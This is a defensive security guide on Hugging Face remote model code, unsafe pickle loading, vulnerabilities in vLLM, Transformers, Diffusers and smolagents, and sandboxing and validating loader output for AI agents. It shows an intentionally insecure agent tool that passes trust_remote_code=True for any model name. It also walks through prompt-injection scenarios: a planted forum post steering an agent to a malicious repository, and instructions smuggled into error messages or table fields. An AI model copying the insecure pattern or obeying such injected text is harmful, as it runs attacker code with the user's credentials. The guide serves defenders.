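The `auto_map` entry gives the class for each part of the model and the file that contains it. The first file could be very short:

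```python
from transformers import PreTrainedConfig

print("configuration_rain was imported")

class RainConfig(PreTrainedConfig):
    model_type = "rain"
```

Calling `AutoModel.from_pretrained("example/rain", trust_remote_code=True)` then does the following:

1. It downloads `config.json` and parses it.
2. It finds `auto_map` and checks whether the caller has allowed remote code.
3. It downloads `configuration_rain.py`, along with any other files in the repository that this one imports, and copies them into a cache folder.
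4. It imports the file. Every top-level statement runs, including the `print` line.
5. It creates a `RainConfig`, which runs any `__init__` method in the class.
6. It imports `modeling_rain.py` in the same way, builds the model and loads the weights.

In step 4, the loader in Hugging Face's *dynamic_module_utils* imports the repository's code with an ordinary call to `importlib.import_module`. The code therefore runs with the same rights as the program that loads the model.

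Safetensors weights don't prevent this, because the program imports the code before it opens the weights. The code also runs after loading, because the program calls `RainModel`'s `forward` method to do the model's calculations every time it uses the model.

A repository can also refer to code in a second repository by putting the second repository's name and two hyphens before the class, as Hugging Face's *Customizing models* shows. For example, `"AutoModel": "other-lab/rain-code--modeling_rain.RainModel"` makes Transformers fetch the model class from `other-lab/rain-code`. Someone who reviews only the first repository would not see that code.

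PyTorch Hub, an older way of sharing models, runs a file called `hubconf.py` from the repository. The name of its `trust_repo` setting is misleading, because `trust_repo=False` makes PyTorch prompt the user for permission to run the code instead of blocking it. An agent that can type into a terminal could answer yes.

### Why model authors include code

Some model repositories include their own code, mainly because the Transformers library can build only the architectures it already contains. A research group with a new attention mechanism (the part of a model that relates words to each other) can ask the library's maintainers to add it, but that takes time. If the group puts the code in the repository, people can use the model on the day it comes out. Otherwise, each user would have to rewrite the code from a description, and small mistakes can make the model perform badly without raising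 an error.

Remote model code has an advantage over a pickle because it is ordinary Python source that anyone can read, with a history of changes. Developers also run strangers' code whenever they install a package from PyPI, so a blanket ban on remote model code would be hard to defend.

Loading a model with `from_pretrained` differs from installing a package in two practical ways. Developers usually choose packages themselves and can fix their versions in a lock file. A model's name may come from a user or a language model, and the default version is whatever the repository's main branch contains at that moment.

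### How common repository code is

In *An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution in Machine Learning Model Hosting*, Siddiq, Romel and colleagues (2026) examined five model-sharing platforms. They counted a repository as having custom code if it had the `custom_code` tag or contained a Python file with one of the usual names, such as `hubconf.py` or one beginning with `modeling_`. For OpenMMLab, which uses its own loading library, they counted every repository.

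| Platform | Repositories with custom code | Of those, flagged by Semgrep | Platform's main safeguard |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hugging Face | 36,697 of 2,107,935 (1.74%) | 1,691 (4.60%) | Scans each upload for known malware, and shows warnings |
| OpenCSG | 6,165 of 192,556 (3.20%) | 280 (4.54%) | Community guidelines |
| ModelScope | 3,193 of 68,736 (4.65%) | 509 (15.94%) | A warning after the download |
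| OpenMMLab | 16 of 16 | 2 (12.50%) | Maintainers review each contribution |
| PyTorch Hub | 26 of 26 | 10 (38.46%) | A prompt before loading |

More than 98% of the repositories on Hugging Face therefore had no custom code by this measure. A tool that refuses remote code can still load most models, although the ones it can't load probably include a disproportionate share of the new models people most want to try. The monthly number of new repositories with custom code rose from double digits in late 2022 to a peak of 4,898 in April 2025. Siddiq and colleagues link the peak to the releases of Llama 4 and Qwen 3 that month, but their only evidence is the timing.

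The 1.74% probably includes many models that don't need their custom code. Siddiq and colleagues give the example of DeepSeek-R1, whose repository has its own configuration class, `DeepseekV3Config`. Transformers now has a built-in class of the same name, according to Hugging Face's *Auto Classes*. The repository's Python files remained useful for people with older versions of the library, but a developer with a current version can leave the flag off. Turning it on can make Transformers run the repository's copy instead of the built-in one.

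In October 2025, the researchers found that none of the five platforms ran custom code in a sandbox when a user loaded a model. Hugging Face had the most safeguards. Its verified badges confirm which organization owns an account, but they don't mean anyone has audited the code.

### What the scans of repository code found

The repositories contained 128,487 Python files, many of them old scripts or utilities not used to load a model. To exclude these, the researchers started from the files that a loader imports and traced which functions and modules the code could reach from there. This left 67,009 files, about 52%.

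They then ran several analysers on those files. On Hugging Face, about 65% of the weaknesses that Semgrep categorized were unsafe deserialization (1,737 findings), and another 19% were uses of `eval`, which runs text as Python code. So some repositories have both problems, with custom code that also loads pickles. Semgrep's most frequent warning overall was about using NumPy inside PyTorch models, which mainly affects speed and portability.

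These warnings are **code smells**, patterns that often accompany mistakes but aren't always exploitable. An `eval` is exploitable only if an outsider controls the text that reaches it and gains something they didn't already have. A repository's author gains nothing from an `eval` in their own file, because the file can already run any Python code. The `eval` matters if it lets a third party run code, for example through a prompt that a user sends to the model.

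Many of the warnings were probably false alarms as well. `assert` statements alone made up 78% of Bandit's findings. Bandit also reported 10,097 hard-coded passwords in the Hugging Face code, but its password check also matches variable names that contain "token". In language-model code a token is usually a piece of text, so a harmless line like `pad_token = "pad"` triggers the warning. The same confusion may explain much of CodeQL's output, since over 98% of its Hugging Face alerts flagged secret comparisons that leak timing information.

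Smells are also a poor way to find malicious repositories, because code that reads a file and sends it to a server can use the same functions as code that reads a vocabulary file and downloads an update.

The researchers therefore also looked for known malicious patterns with YARA, a tool that compares files with malware signatures. It found matches in 2,562 of the Hugging Face repositories (6.98%), but 82.54% of the matches were for a 3D graphics file format, which a Python file can't be. The next most common matches were for code that detects virtual machines, which malware sometimes includes to avoid analysis. However, the signatures for two different virtual machines each matched exactly 1,260 times, which suggests that the same harmless text triggered both. The paper's results section says that the matches are not confirmed malware, but its conclusion refers to "malicious code" in this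 category, which the evidence doesn't support.

Four scanners for malware and unsafe weights files (ClamAV, PickleScan, ModelScan and ModelAudit) found nothing in the loading code. Siddiq and colleagues explain that these tools mainly examine weights files rather than Python source. A clean scan on a model's page is therefore little evidence that its `modeling_` file is safe.

The study is strong evidence that repository code is common and often carelessly written, but it doesn't report how much of it is malicious. It does cite earlier research that found 91 malicious models and nine malicious dataset scripts.

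### What developers misunderstand about the flag

The researchers also read 612 discussions about `trust_remote_code` and `trust_repo`. Most (519) were GitHub issues and proposed code changes, so the discussions mainly come from people who had run into a problem.

Many of these people just wanted the model to load. They reported that a pipeline ignored the flag, or that a hosting service didn't allow it. To avoid the flag, others asked Transformers' maintainers to add a model to the library, or edited the model's files by hand. Some worried about malicious code or couldn't tell which files they were agreeing to run.

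The most worrying problem is that some developers misunderstood the flag. Some thought it only allowed the library to read a model's metadata. Others thought that turning it on also pinned the model's version, and that pinning the version also turned it on. A developer with either belief could turn on the flag without realizing that this lets the model's code run.

### When vLLM ran repository code without permission

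Leaving the flag off has not always been enough. Between December 2025 and July 2026, public databases recorded at least seven flaws that let a repository run code even though the user had not allowed it:

| Software | Identifier | Why the code ran anyway | Fixed in |
|---|---|---|---|
| vLLM | CVE-2025-66448 | One configuration class never checked the flag | 0.11.1 |
| vLLM | CVE-2026-22807 | The server didn't check it at startup | 0.14.0 |
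| vLLM | CVE-2026-27893 | Two model files always set it to `True` | 0.18.0 |
| Transformers | CVE-2026-4372 | Another configuration field could also name code | 5.3.0 |
| Transformers | CVE-2026-5241 | The repository's configuration overrode the user's choice | 5.5.0 |
| Diffusers | CVE-2026-44513 | The check was in the download step, which some calls skipped | 0.38.0 |
| Diffusers | CVE-2026-45804 | Files could change between the check and the import | 0.38.0 |

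The first flaw was in vLLM's support for one of NVIDIA's Nemotron models. According to NVD's *CVE-2025-66448 Detail*, the configuration class followed any `auto_map` entry and immediately created an instance of the class it found. An attacker could publish a harmless-looking repository whose `auto_map` pointed to another containing malicious code. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2015* (2026) adds that the faulty code was in a common loading path, so the flaw could affect automated tests and developers' computers as well as servers.

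The second flaw was broader. NVD's *CVE-2026-22807 Detail* (2026) describes how vLLM followed `auto_map` entries, and ran the code they pointed to, while working out what kind of model it had been given. This happened before the server accepted any requests, so requiring a login on its API gave no protection.

Someone found the third flaw after both fixes were in place. Two model files passed `trust_remote_code=True` to Transformers regardless of the user's setting, according to OSV's *GHSA-7972-pg2x-xr59* (2026). Red Hat's *CVE-2026-4944* page describes the same flaw under another number and notes that it mainly affects installations that load NemotronVL or Kimi K2.5 models. That is reassuring if the server's administrator chooses the model, but less so if strangers can influence the choice, because the author of a malicious repository also writes its `config.json` and can declare one of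 those two architectures.

The flaws kept coming back because every function between the command line and the import has to pass on the user's decision, and each new model file can fail to do so. vLLM's helper function for loading these classes originally had no `trust_remote_code` parameter. The newer version, on vLLM's *dynamic_module* page, requires the parameter and checks it first, so a programmer who forgets it gets an error. The check still doesn't protect the user if the caller passes `True`, as the two model files did when they called Transformers, so it is worth searching the installed packages for `trust_remote_code=True`.

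Most of these records don't mention deserialization. NVD classifies the first two vLLM flaws as CWE-94, code injection, so a team that filters advisories by CWE-502 will miss them.

### Similar flaws in Transformers and Diffusers

The Transformers flaw with the widest reach was CVE-2026-4372. The library copied every field of `config.json` onto an internal object, including fields that only the library was supposed to set. One of those fields could name a repository of **kernels**, which are pieces of optimized code for a model's calculations. The library would then download the package and import it without checking `trust_remote_code`.

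Sources disagree about which installations of transformers were affected. GCVE lists every version before 5.3.0. *Unauthenticated remote code execution in HuggingFace transformers via config injection*, by Pluto Security, the company that found the flaw, limits it to versions 4.56.0 to 5.2.x with the optional `kernels` package installed. Pluto Security's account is more convincing because it identifies the release that introduced the faulty code.

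Pluto Security also counts about 232 million downloads of vulnerable versions in the six months before the fix. That greatly overstates the number of machines at risk, because automated systems download the same package repeatedly and `kernels` had only about 1.7 million downloads in the same period. The company plausibly argues that installations of `kernels` matter more than most, since they tend to be on servers with graphics processors and cloud credentials.

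Users were slow to adopt the fix. It came out in version 5.3.0 on 4 March 2026, but the flaw wasn't widely known until Pluto Security disclosed it in June, as SiliconANGLE's *Critical Hugging Face Transformers flaw ran attacker code on a routine model* (2026) reported. Nearly three months after the release, vulnerable versions still made up around 23% of weekly downloads.

The other Transformers flaw was in LightGlue, a model that matches points between two images. Its configuration can contain a second model's configuration. According to OSV's *CVE-2026-5241* (2026), when the library loaded this second configuration, data from the repository replaced the user's `trust_remote_code=False`. The repository's code could therefore run even though the user had disallowed it. GitLab lists all versions before 5.5.0 as affected.

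Diffusers, Hugging Face's library for image-generating models, had its check for repository code in the download function instead of at the import. GitLab's *CVE-2026-44513* (2026) traces three variants of a flaw to this placement. In one variant, the caller named a second repository for the code, but the library checked the first repository's list of files, according to Enginsight's *CVE-2026-44513*. Enginsight's *CVE-2026-45804* (2026) describes a later flaw, in which Diffusers checked the files and then loaded them from a cached folder whose contents could have changed in the meantime.

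To avoid these flaws, an agent that loads models should use at least vLLM 0.18.0, Transformers 5.5.0 and Diffusers 0.38.0. The flag has failed so often that it shouldn't be the agent's only protection against a stranger's repository.

### An agent tool that takes a model name

This tool labels texts with whatever model the agent chooses:

```python
from transformers import pipeline

def label_text(text, model_name):
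    """Label a text with a model from Hugging Face."""
    classify = pipeline("text-classification", model=model_name,
                        trust_remote_code=True)
    return classify(text)
```

The developer may have added the flag for one useful model that needed it, but it applies to every model name the agent passes. Suppose a user asks the agent to sort a weather club's forum posts by topic, and one post mentions that messages in dialect need a special model, `example-lab/dialect-weather`. If the agent follows the suggestion, the tool downloads that repository and imports its code in the host process. If the code is malicious, it can still build a working model, so the user may get sensible labels and notice nothing.

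Setting the flag to `False` is a big improvement, but the tool would still let strangers choose the model. They could exploit an unpatched flaw like the ones above, a pickled weights file in an older installation, or a hostile chat template. The name can also be a path to a local folder, so a tool that saves downloads could supply the repository. It is safer to let the agent choose only from a fixed table:

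```python
MODELS = {
    "weather-topics": (
        "example/weather-topics",
        "3f1c0d5e8a7b42964d0e1f2a3b4c5d6e7f801234"),
}

def label_text(text, model_name):
    """Label a text with an approved model."""
    if model_name not in MODELS:
        raise ValueError("unknown model")
    repo, commit = MODELS[model_name]
    classify = pipeline("text-classification", model=repo,
                        revision=commit, trust_remote_code=False,
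                        model_kwargs={"use_safetensors": True})
    return classify(text)
```

The tool should never expose `trust_remote_code` as a parameter. An agent that gets an error about custom code is likely to try again with the flag on, especially since Transformers' error message includes that fix. It is also better to write `trust_remote_code=False` than to leave the argument out, because some versions then show a yes-or-no question in the terminal, which an agent might answer.

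None of this restrains a coding agent that writes and runs its own Python, because it can call `from_pretrained` with any arguments. Such an agent needs a sandbox, preferably one that can download models only from a server with approved copies.

The `print` line in `configuration_rain.py` can be used to test whether the flag blocks the repository's code. A developer can put that file and its `config.json` in a local folder, load the folder with the flag on to confirm that the message appears, and then load it in a new process with the flag off. The second attempt should raise an error without printing the message. Repeating the test after each upgrade can catch a broken check in that loading path, though not in others.

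### Whether to allow a particular repository

When someone asks for a model that comes with its own code, these steps avoid most of the risk:

1. **Look for a built-in architecture.** If the `model_type` in `config.json` is on the list in Hugging Face's *Auto Classes*, the model will probably load with the flag off. If it isn't on the list, a newer version of Transformers may have added it.
2. **Read the code.** If nobody on the team can do this, the answer should be no.
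3. **Pin the commit**, including the commit of any second repository.
4. **Keep a copy** on storage that the agent can't change.
5. **Load it outside the host process**, in a sandbox without credentials.

Step 1 is often enough. The current list includes `deepseek_v3` and `kimi_k25`, for example, so waiting a few weeks for library support can make the other steps unnecessary.

#### Reading the code

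Hugging Face advises users to turn the flag on only for repositories that they trust and whose code they have read. Downloading the files doesn't run them:

```python
from huggingface_hub import snapshot_download

snapshot_download("example/rain", revision=COMMIT,
                  allow_patterns=["*.json", "*.py"],
                  local_dir="review")
```

The reviewer should search all the JSON files for `auto_map`, because the tokenizer can have its own entry in a separate file. An entry containing `--` points to another repository, which needs the same review. The reviewer should then read each file that `auto_map` names and any files they import.

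Model code mostly does arithmetic on tensors, and a configuration class mostly stores settings. Code in these files stands out and needs a good explanation if it starts programs, opens network connections, reads environment variables, decodes long strings, or calls `eval` or a pickle loader.

A repository's popularity is a poor substitute for reading its code. Pluto Security describes a malicious repository that reached first place on Hugging Face's trending list in 2026, with about 244,000 downloads in under 18 hours. The attack still required the user to run a script by hand.

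#### Pinning the code

Pinning guards against later changes to the code, such as those made by an attacker who takes over the author's account. Hugging Face's *Loading models* recommends passing a commit hash, which identifies one exact state of the repository, as the `revision`. The `revision` can also be a branch name or tag, but the repository's owner can move these to different code.

`revision` covers only the repository in the call. If the code is in a second repository, it needs a separate argument:

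```python
model = AutoModel.from_pretrained(
    "example/rain",
    revision=MODEL_COMMIT,       # config.json and weights
    code_revision=CODE_COMMIT,   # Python files in the second repository
    trust_remote_code=True,
)
```

Without `code_revision`, Transformers uses the newest version of the second repository's code, even though the first repository is pinned. The tokenizer is loaded by its own `from_pretrained` call, which must be pinned too.

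Pinned code can still download other files when it runs. In the study by Siddiq and colleagues, Bandit found 3,803 places in the Hugging Face code that downloaded files from the site unsafely, usually without a fixed version. A reviewer should replace such downloads with pinned ones or local files.

#### Keeping a copy

A copy on the team's own storage protects against deletion as well as changes. If the copied repository's `auto_map` refers to a second repository, Transformers will still fetch that code from Hugging Face, so the developer has to copy those Python files too and remove the second repository's name from the `auto_map` entries. The developer can then set the environment variable `HF_HUB_OFFLINE=1`, which makes downloads fail, to check whether anything still depends on the site.

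As with agent checkpoints, the agent's other tools must not be able to write to this copy or to the cache folder for Python modules.

The best arrangement for a model that a team uses regularly is to move the reviewed Python files into the team's own code:

```python
from our_models.modeling_rain import RainModel   # reviewed copy

model = RainModel.from_pretrained("/srv/models/rain",
                                  use_safetensors=True)
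```

The program now imports the class directly, so it doesn't need `auto_map` or the flag. Changes to the code go through the same review as the rest of the program. But the team has to maintain the files and copy over any fixes from the original author.

#### When convenience is a good enough reason

A researcher who wants to try a new model for an afternoon doesn't need all of this. They can reasonably run it with the flag on if they use a temporary machine that holds no credentials or private data, because there is little there for malicious code to steal. If the machine can reach an internal network, it is still wise to read the code first.

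The same choice is much harder to justify in an agent's host process. The flag saves a developer perhaps a few hours of reviewing and copying files, but it gives the repository's author access to everything the agent can use, for as long as the tool exists. Some teams will still need a model without built-in support, and they can use a reviewed, pinned copy without giving the agent general permission to run code from repositories.

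## Isolating a loader and controlling what it sends back

Sometimes a team can't avoid an unsafe loader, for example because a customer's records exist only as old pickles. The team can then run the loader in a sandbox, where code from a malicious file can do little damage. But the sandbox has to return a result to the host process, and if the host loads that result unsafely, the attacker can run code there too.

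### Running a converter in a container

Suppose a weather club sends pickled tables to an agent. A small converter can load each one and write it out as JSON:

```python
# convert.py
import io, sys
import pandas as pd

table = pd.read_pickle(io.BytesIO(sys.stdin.buffer.read()))
sys.stdout.write(table.to_json(orient="split", index=False))
```

Any call in the pickle happens inside the converter. This command runs it in a Docker container, using an image (`table-converter`) that contains only Python, pandas and `convert.py`:

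```
docker run --rm -i --name convert-1 --pull never \
  --network none --read-only \
  --user 65534:65534 --cap-drop ALL \
  --security-opt no-new-privileges \
  --memory 1g --memory-swap 1g --cpus 1 --pids-limit 128 \
  table-converter < table.pkl | head -c 5000001 > reply.json
```

The container receives the pickle as a stream of bytes, so it needs no access to the host's folders. `head` cuts the reply off at one byte over the host's 5 MB limit.

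Pigment (2026), a company that built a sandbox for code written by language models, lists the main risks as reading sensitive data, calling internal services, sending data out and using up computing resources. These settings limit them:

| Setting | How to apply it | What it limits |
|---|---|---|
| No credentials | No keys in the image, in `-e` options or in mounted files | Theft of keys |
| No network | `--network none` | Sending data out, downloading more code, calling internal services |
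| Read-only files | `--read-only`, and no mounted folders | Changes to the converter or the host's files |
| Unprivileged user | `--user`, `--cap-drop ALL`, `no-new-privileges` | Use of administrator rights to break out |
| Resource caps | `--memory`, `--cpus`, `--pids-limit` | Slowing down or crashing the host |
| Time cap | A timer on the host that runs `docker kill convert-1` | Files that never finish loading |
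| Disposal | `--rm`, and a new container for each file | One file's code affecting the next file |

Removing the loader's credentials and network access matters most. Malicious code can then read little except the file it came in, and can send data out only through the loader's reply. On a cloud server, `--network none` also blocks the metadata service, from which programs can often fetch temporary credentials. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) includes environment variables and credential stores in its attack tests because they are common targets.

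The timer has to stop the container itself, since ending the `docker run` command can leave the container running. The account that starts containers also needs protection, because access to Docker usually gives full control of the host. Starting the converter from a small separate service is safer because it keeps Docker access away from the agent's other tools.

### Processes, containers and virtual machines

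The three usual kinds of isolation differ mainly in what the sandbox shares with the host:

| | Separate process | Container | Virtual machine |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shares with the host | The kernel (the core of the operating system) and, by default, the user account, files and network | The kernel | The hardware, through a hypervisor |
| What an attacker needs to get out | Often nothing, unless the developer adds restrictions | A kernel flaw or a configuration mistake | A hypervisor flaw or a configuration mistake |
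| Cost | Very low | An image to maintain, and usually under a second to start | More memory, a second operating system to maintain, and often a slower start |

**A separate process** protects the host from crashes but by itself does little against malicious code. On Linux, it can usually read the host process's environment variables if both run under the same account, even if the developer starts it with an empty environment. It needs its own account and operating-system restrictions on file and network access. Stopping it can also be difficult. Pydantic notes that killing a worker in its own process pool would not stop any process the worker had started.

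Restricting Python inside the host process is weaker still. smolagents, Hugging Face's library for agents that write their actions as Python code, has a `LocalPythonExecutor` that limits imports and built-in functions. NVD's *CVE-2025-5120 Detail* describes how code could escape the executor through modules and functions it permitted. OSV's *CVE-2025-9959* (2025) records another escape that required a prompt injection. The documentation for version 1.25.0 still called the executor suitable for untrusted code, but the project description for the same release, Hugging Face's *smolagents 1.25.0* (2026), warned against this use.

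A container with the settings above is a reasonable choice for a team's internal tool. For a service that opens files from many strangers, a virtual machine is worth the extra overhead, because with containers a single kernel flaw would expose the host and every other user's data.

*Add Blaxel support for remote code execution* (Joffref, cploujoux and Larcher) reports that virtual machines from the cloud service Blaxel start from hibernation in under 25 milliseconds. But a hibernating machine keeps its memory, so reusing one for another person's file would undo the benefit of discarding machines after use. The figure doesn't show how long a new machine takes to start.

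A developer also has to decide how much of the agent to isolate. Joffref and colleagues explain that running the whole agent in a sandbox gives better isolation but may require putting API keys inside it. Running only the generated code in the sandbox keeps the keys outside, but data then has to pass between the sandbox and the host. Willison (2026), in *59 posts tagged “sandboxing”*, calls the second arrangement an external sandbox. This setup suits a loader well, as long as the host treats every reply as untrusted.

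### How a reply could run code on a smolagents host

smolagents has remote executors for external sandboxes, and their return path was unsafe. A run works roughly like this:

1. The host process sends the agent's variables to the sandbox.
2. The model writes Python code, and the sandbox runs it.
3. The sandbox serializes the result and sends it back.
4. The executor object in the host process rebuilds the result.

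Affected versions exchanged values as pickles. If a web page led the model to write malicious code, that code could replace the result in step 3 with its own pickle, which would run on the host in step 4 even if the sandbox worked perfectly.

The advisories for this flaw, CVE-2025-14931, suggest that the host is the vulnerable side, though they don't say so explicitly. Aikido's *smolagents is vulnerable to Deserialization of Untrusted Data* (2026) locates the code execution in "the executor process", and the executor is the part of the library that runs beside the agent. Hugging Face's *Python code executors* advises developers to allow pickle only if they "fully trust the execution environment", which makes sense only if the host loads what the environment sends.

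OSV's *PYSEC-2026-543* (2026) gives the flaw the maximum severity score of 10.0, based on a remote attacker needing no login or user action. In the attack above, someone also has to influence the code in the sandbox, usually through prompt injection, so 10.0 is probably too high for an agent that reads only its owner's files, though it is more reasonable for one that browses the web.

The flaw took a long time to fix. *huggingface / smolagents*, a page on the bug bounty service huntr, lists two reports of unsafe pickle loading from June and July 2025, both marked "informative". Their titles don't show whether they concerned the same code. According to Zero Day Initiative's *(0Day) Hugging Face smolagents Remote Python Executor Deserialization of Untrusted Data* (2025), researchers submitted a report on 9 December, the bounty program rejected it as out of scope, and the vendor closed it as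 a duplicate. Zero Day Initiative published the flaw on 18 December without a fix.

Developers can easily make the same mistake with Python's standard library. `ProcessPoolExecutor` and `multiprocessing` return results from worker processes as pickles, so a malicious file loaded in a worker can still attack the host through the reply. Starting `convert.py` with `subprocess` and reading JSON from its output avoids this. LeRobot's client had the same problem between machines, and OSV lists both the client and its server as vulnerable.

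### How smolagents fixed it, and in which release

smolagents now uses a component called `SafeSerializer`, which converts values to JSON and puts `safe:` in front of them. If a value doesn't fit the JSON format, the library raises an error. Developers who need the old behaviour can set `allow_pickle=True`, which lets the library fall back to pickle and mark the data with `pickle:`. According to Aikido, the new code also refuses data with no prefix, so an old-style pickle can't slip through.

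Refusing to load pickles protects the receiver, because whoever controls the sandbox also chooses the reply's prefix. With `allow_pickle=True`, malicious code can send a `pickle:` reply even when JSON would have worked. A developer who gets a serialization error should therefore leave the setting off and change what the sandbox returns, for example by converting a custom object to a dictionary.

Sources disagree about the affected versions:

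- CIRCL's *GHSA-q9r5-6hrr-9ph7*, a copy of GitHub's advisory, gives 1.23.0 as the last affected version. OSV does the same and lists no fix.
- Aikido lists 1.24.0 as affected and 1.25.0 as the fix.
- Snyk lists every version as affected, with no fix.

**Version 1.25.0 is the safe minimum.** Its documentation describes the new serializer, with pickle off by default. The release came out on 14 May 2026, a week after GitHub reviewed its advisory, so GitHub listed no fix at that point. Version 1.23.0 was probably the newest version when researchers reported the flaw. A scanner that relies on OSV could therefore miss the flaw in 1.24.0, while one that relies on Snyk's data would raise a false alarm for 1.25.0.

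The change to safe defaults seems to have taken several steps. Hugging Face's *smolagents* repository has a commit titled "Set allow_pickle default to False in internal calls", which suggests that some of the library's own calls had still permitted pickle. After upgrading, a team may want to search both the installed package and its own code for `allow_pickle=True`.

smolagents also lets developers apply many of the sandbox settings above. Its Docker executor passes extra options to the container through `container_run_kwargs`. It communicates with the container over a network port, so `--network none` would break it, and blocking outgoing connections requires a firewall. The Blaxel executor has settings for memory and lifetime, and the WebAssembly executor stops code after 60 seconds by default. Using the agent in a `with` block cleans up the sandbox afterwards.

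### Checking the converted table

A valid `reply.json` from the weather converter looks like this:

```json
{"columns": ["city", "celsius"], "data": [["Oslo", 7], ["Bergen", 9]]}
```

The host can't assume that `convert.py` wrote it, because code in the pickle may have written something else to the output. It has to check the size, columns and types before using the table:

```python
import json

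MAX_BYTES = 5_000_000
MAX_ROWS = 50_000

def check_table(raw):
    if len(raw) > MAX_BYTES:
        raise ValueError("reply too large")
    try:
        table = json.loads(raw)
    except (ValueError, RecursionError):
        raise ValueError("invalid JSON") from None
    if not isinstance(table, dict) or set(table) != {"columns", "data"}:
        raise ValueError("unexpected fields")
    if table["columns"] != ["city", "celsius"]:
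        raise ValueError("unexpected columns")
    rows = table["data"]
    if not isinstance(rows, list) or len(rows) > MAX_ROWS:
        raise ValueError("expected a list of at most 50,000 rows")
    for row in rows:
        if not isinstance(row, list) or len(row) != 2:
            raise ValueError("unexpected row")
        city, celsius = row
        if not isinstance(city, str) or len(city) > 100:
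            raise ValueError("invalid city")
        if type(celsius) not in (int, float) or not -100 <= celsius <= 70:
            raise ValueError("invalid temperature")
    return rows
```

The range check also rejects `NaN` ("not a number"), which Python's JSON loader accepts. If the container stops early, the reply is incomplete and fails to parse as JSON.

For larger tables, Arrow is faster than JSON and keeps exact column types. The converter would write an Arrow stream instead, and the host could read it like this:

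```python
import pyarrow as pa

SCHEMA = pa.schema([("city", pa.string()), ("celsius", pa.float64())])

def check_arrow(raw):
    if len(raw) > MAX_BYTES:
        raise ValueError("reply too large")
    reader = pa.ipc.open_stream(raw)
    if reader.schema != SCHEMA:
        raise ValueError("unexpected columns or types")
    table = reader.read_all()
    table.validate(full=True)
    if table.num_rows > MAX_ROWS:
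        raise ValueError("too many rows")
    return table
```

`validate(full=True)` checks that the positions inside the data are consistent. The host still needs to check individual values as it would for JSON. As with Parquet, a small compressed reply may need much more memory once loaded. JSON is better for small tables because its loader is simpler.

If a sandbox returns its result as a file in a shared folder, malicious code could replace that file with a link to one of the host's files, or change it after the host has checked it. The example avoids both problems because the host creates `reply.json` itself. The host should read the file once and use only the values that `check_table` returns.

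Error messages are also part of the return path. If the host passes the container's error output to the language model, an attacker can put instructions for the model in an exception message. The host should send the model a fixed message instead, such as "the file could not be converted".

### Signing data with HMAC

Sometimes a program has to load its own pickles from a place where others can write, such as a shared cache. An HMAC can show whether someone without the secret key has changed them:

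```python
import hmac, pickle

def seal(value, key):
    data = pickle.dumps(value)
    return hmac.digest(key, data, "sha256") + data

def unseal(blob, key):
    tag, data = blob[:32], blob[32:]
    expected = hmac.digest(key, data, "sha256")
    if not hmac.compare_digest(tag, expected):
        raise ValueError("wrong signature")
    return pickle.loads(data)
```

It works like this:

1. The developer creates a random key, for example with `secrets.token_bytes(32)`, and stores it where only this program can read it.
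2. `seal` serializes the value and computes a 32-byte tag from the key and the data.
3. The program stores the tag in front of the data.
4. When loading, `unseal` separates the two and computes the tag again.
5. `compare_digest` compares the tags in a way that doesn't reveal through its timing how much of a false tag is correct.
6. Only if they match does the program unpickle the data.

Changing even one byte of the data produces a different tag, and an outsider can't compute the right one without the key.

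A valid signature proves only that someone with the key signed those bytes. Hugging Face's *Pickle Scanning* likewise says that signed uploads guarantee a file's origin but not its safety.

A sandbox that opens untrusted files must never hold the signing key, because malicious code in a file could use it to sign a pickle that the host would accept. Having the host sign the sandbox's replies doesn't help, because the host would be signing the attacker's bytes. The agent's other tools must not be able to read the key either.

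HMAC also doesn't stop an attacker from replacing a file with an older one that has a valid signature. If that matters, the program can include the file's name and version number in the signed data and check them after verifying the signature. The name and version number should be outside the pickle, so that the program can read them before loading it.

### What can still go wrong

Code in the pickle could produce a valid table with false data, such as one in which every temperature is two degrees too high. The agent should trust the converted table no more than a CSV file from the same sender, and should keep a record of where it came from.

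**The returned text can contain instructions.** A 100-character city field can hold a prompt injection. The host could accept only names from a list of known cities, or calculate an average itself and give the model only that number. Where free text is necessary, the main protection is to limit what the agent can do after reading it.

**The sandbox can have flaws.** *Security of OpenClaw Agents* (2026), a study of an open-source agent, describes mistakes in sandbox rules and path checks that let restricted sessions use host tools and read or write files outside the sandbox. In one type of mistake, the code checked a path but opened it later, which gave an attacker time to change it. Passing data as a stream, as the converter does, removes the need for such path checks.

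Running remote model code in a sandbox raises the same problems. The host has to check every output of the model, whereas a converter handles each file only once.

### What to log

A useful log lets a team find out later which file ran code, where it ran and what it could reach. The host should record:

- the file's hash and source, the user, and the tool call that requested the load
- the loader and the version of the sandbox image
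- how long the load took, how it ended, and whether it reached a memory or time limit
- replies that failed a check, and the reason
- failed signatures and names that a `find_class` allowlist refused
- attempts to open a network connection or start another program, if the sandbox can report them
- changes to settings such as `allow_pickle`

Attempts to use the network or start programs are especially useful signs of a malicious file, because converting a table requires neither. Exceeding a memory or time limit once is weaker evidence, since a large but harmless file can do that too.

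The host should write the log outside the sandbox and send a copy to a machine that the agent can't change. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* includes tampering with the agent's log files among its attacks. The log should not contain secrets, and any text from the file should be escaped, because an attacker could otherwise use line breaks to add false entries.

### Which secrets to replace after a compromise

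The response depends on where the malicious code ran:

| Where the code ran | What to replace |
|---|---|
| In the converter, with all the settings above and no sign of an escape | No secrets, but discard the reply |
| In a sandbox with credentials or network access | Every credential in it, and any that it could have obtained from services on the network |
| In the host process, or in a sandbox that it may have escaped | Every secret that the host process's account could read |

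For a typical agent, the last row covers API keys for language models, tokens for email and source code, database passwords, cloud credentials, SSH keys and HMAC keys. If the code could have gained administrator rights, the row covers every secret on the machine. After an HMAC key is replaced, the program must also reject everything signed with the old one, because the attacker may have used it to sign new files.

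The order of the steps matters:

1. Disconnect the machine from the network. Keep a copy of its disk, the logs and the suspicious file.
2. Revoke the old credentials from a different machine.
3. Check the logs of the services those credentials gave access to. An attacker may have created new keys or accounts that would survive the replacement.
4. Rebuild the host from a clean image and fix the unsafe loader.
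5. Delete or restore from a clean backup anything the code could have changed, including caches, agent checkpoints and downloaded models.
6. Put new credentials on the rebuilt machine.

Putting new keys on the old machine could let the attacker steal those too.
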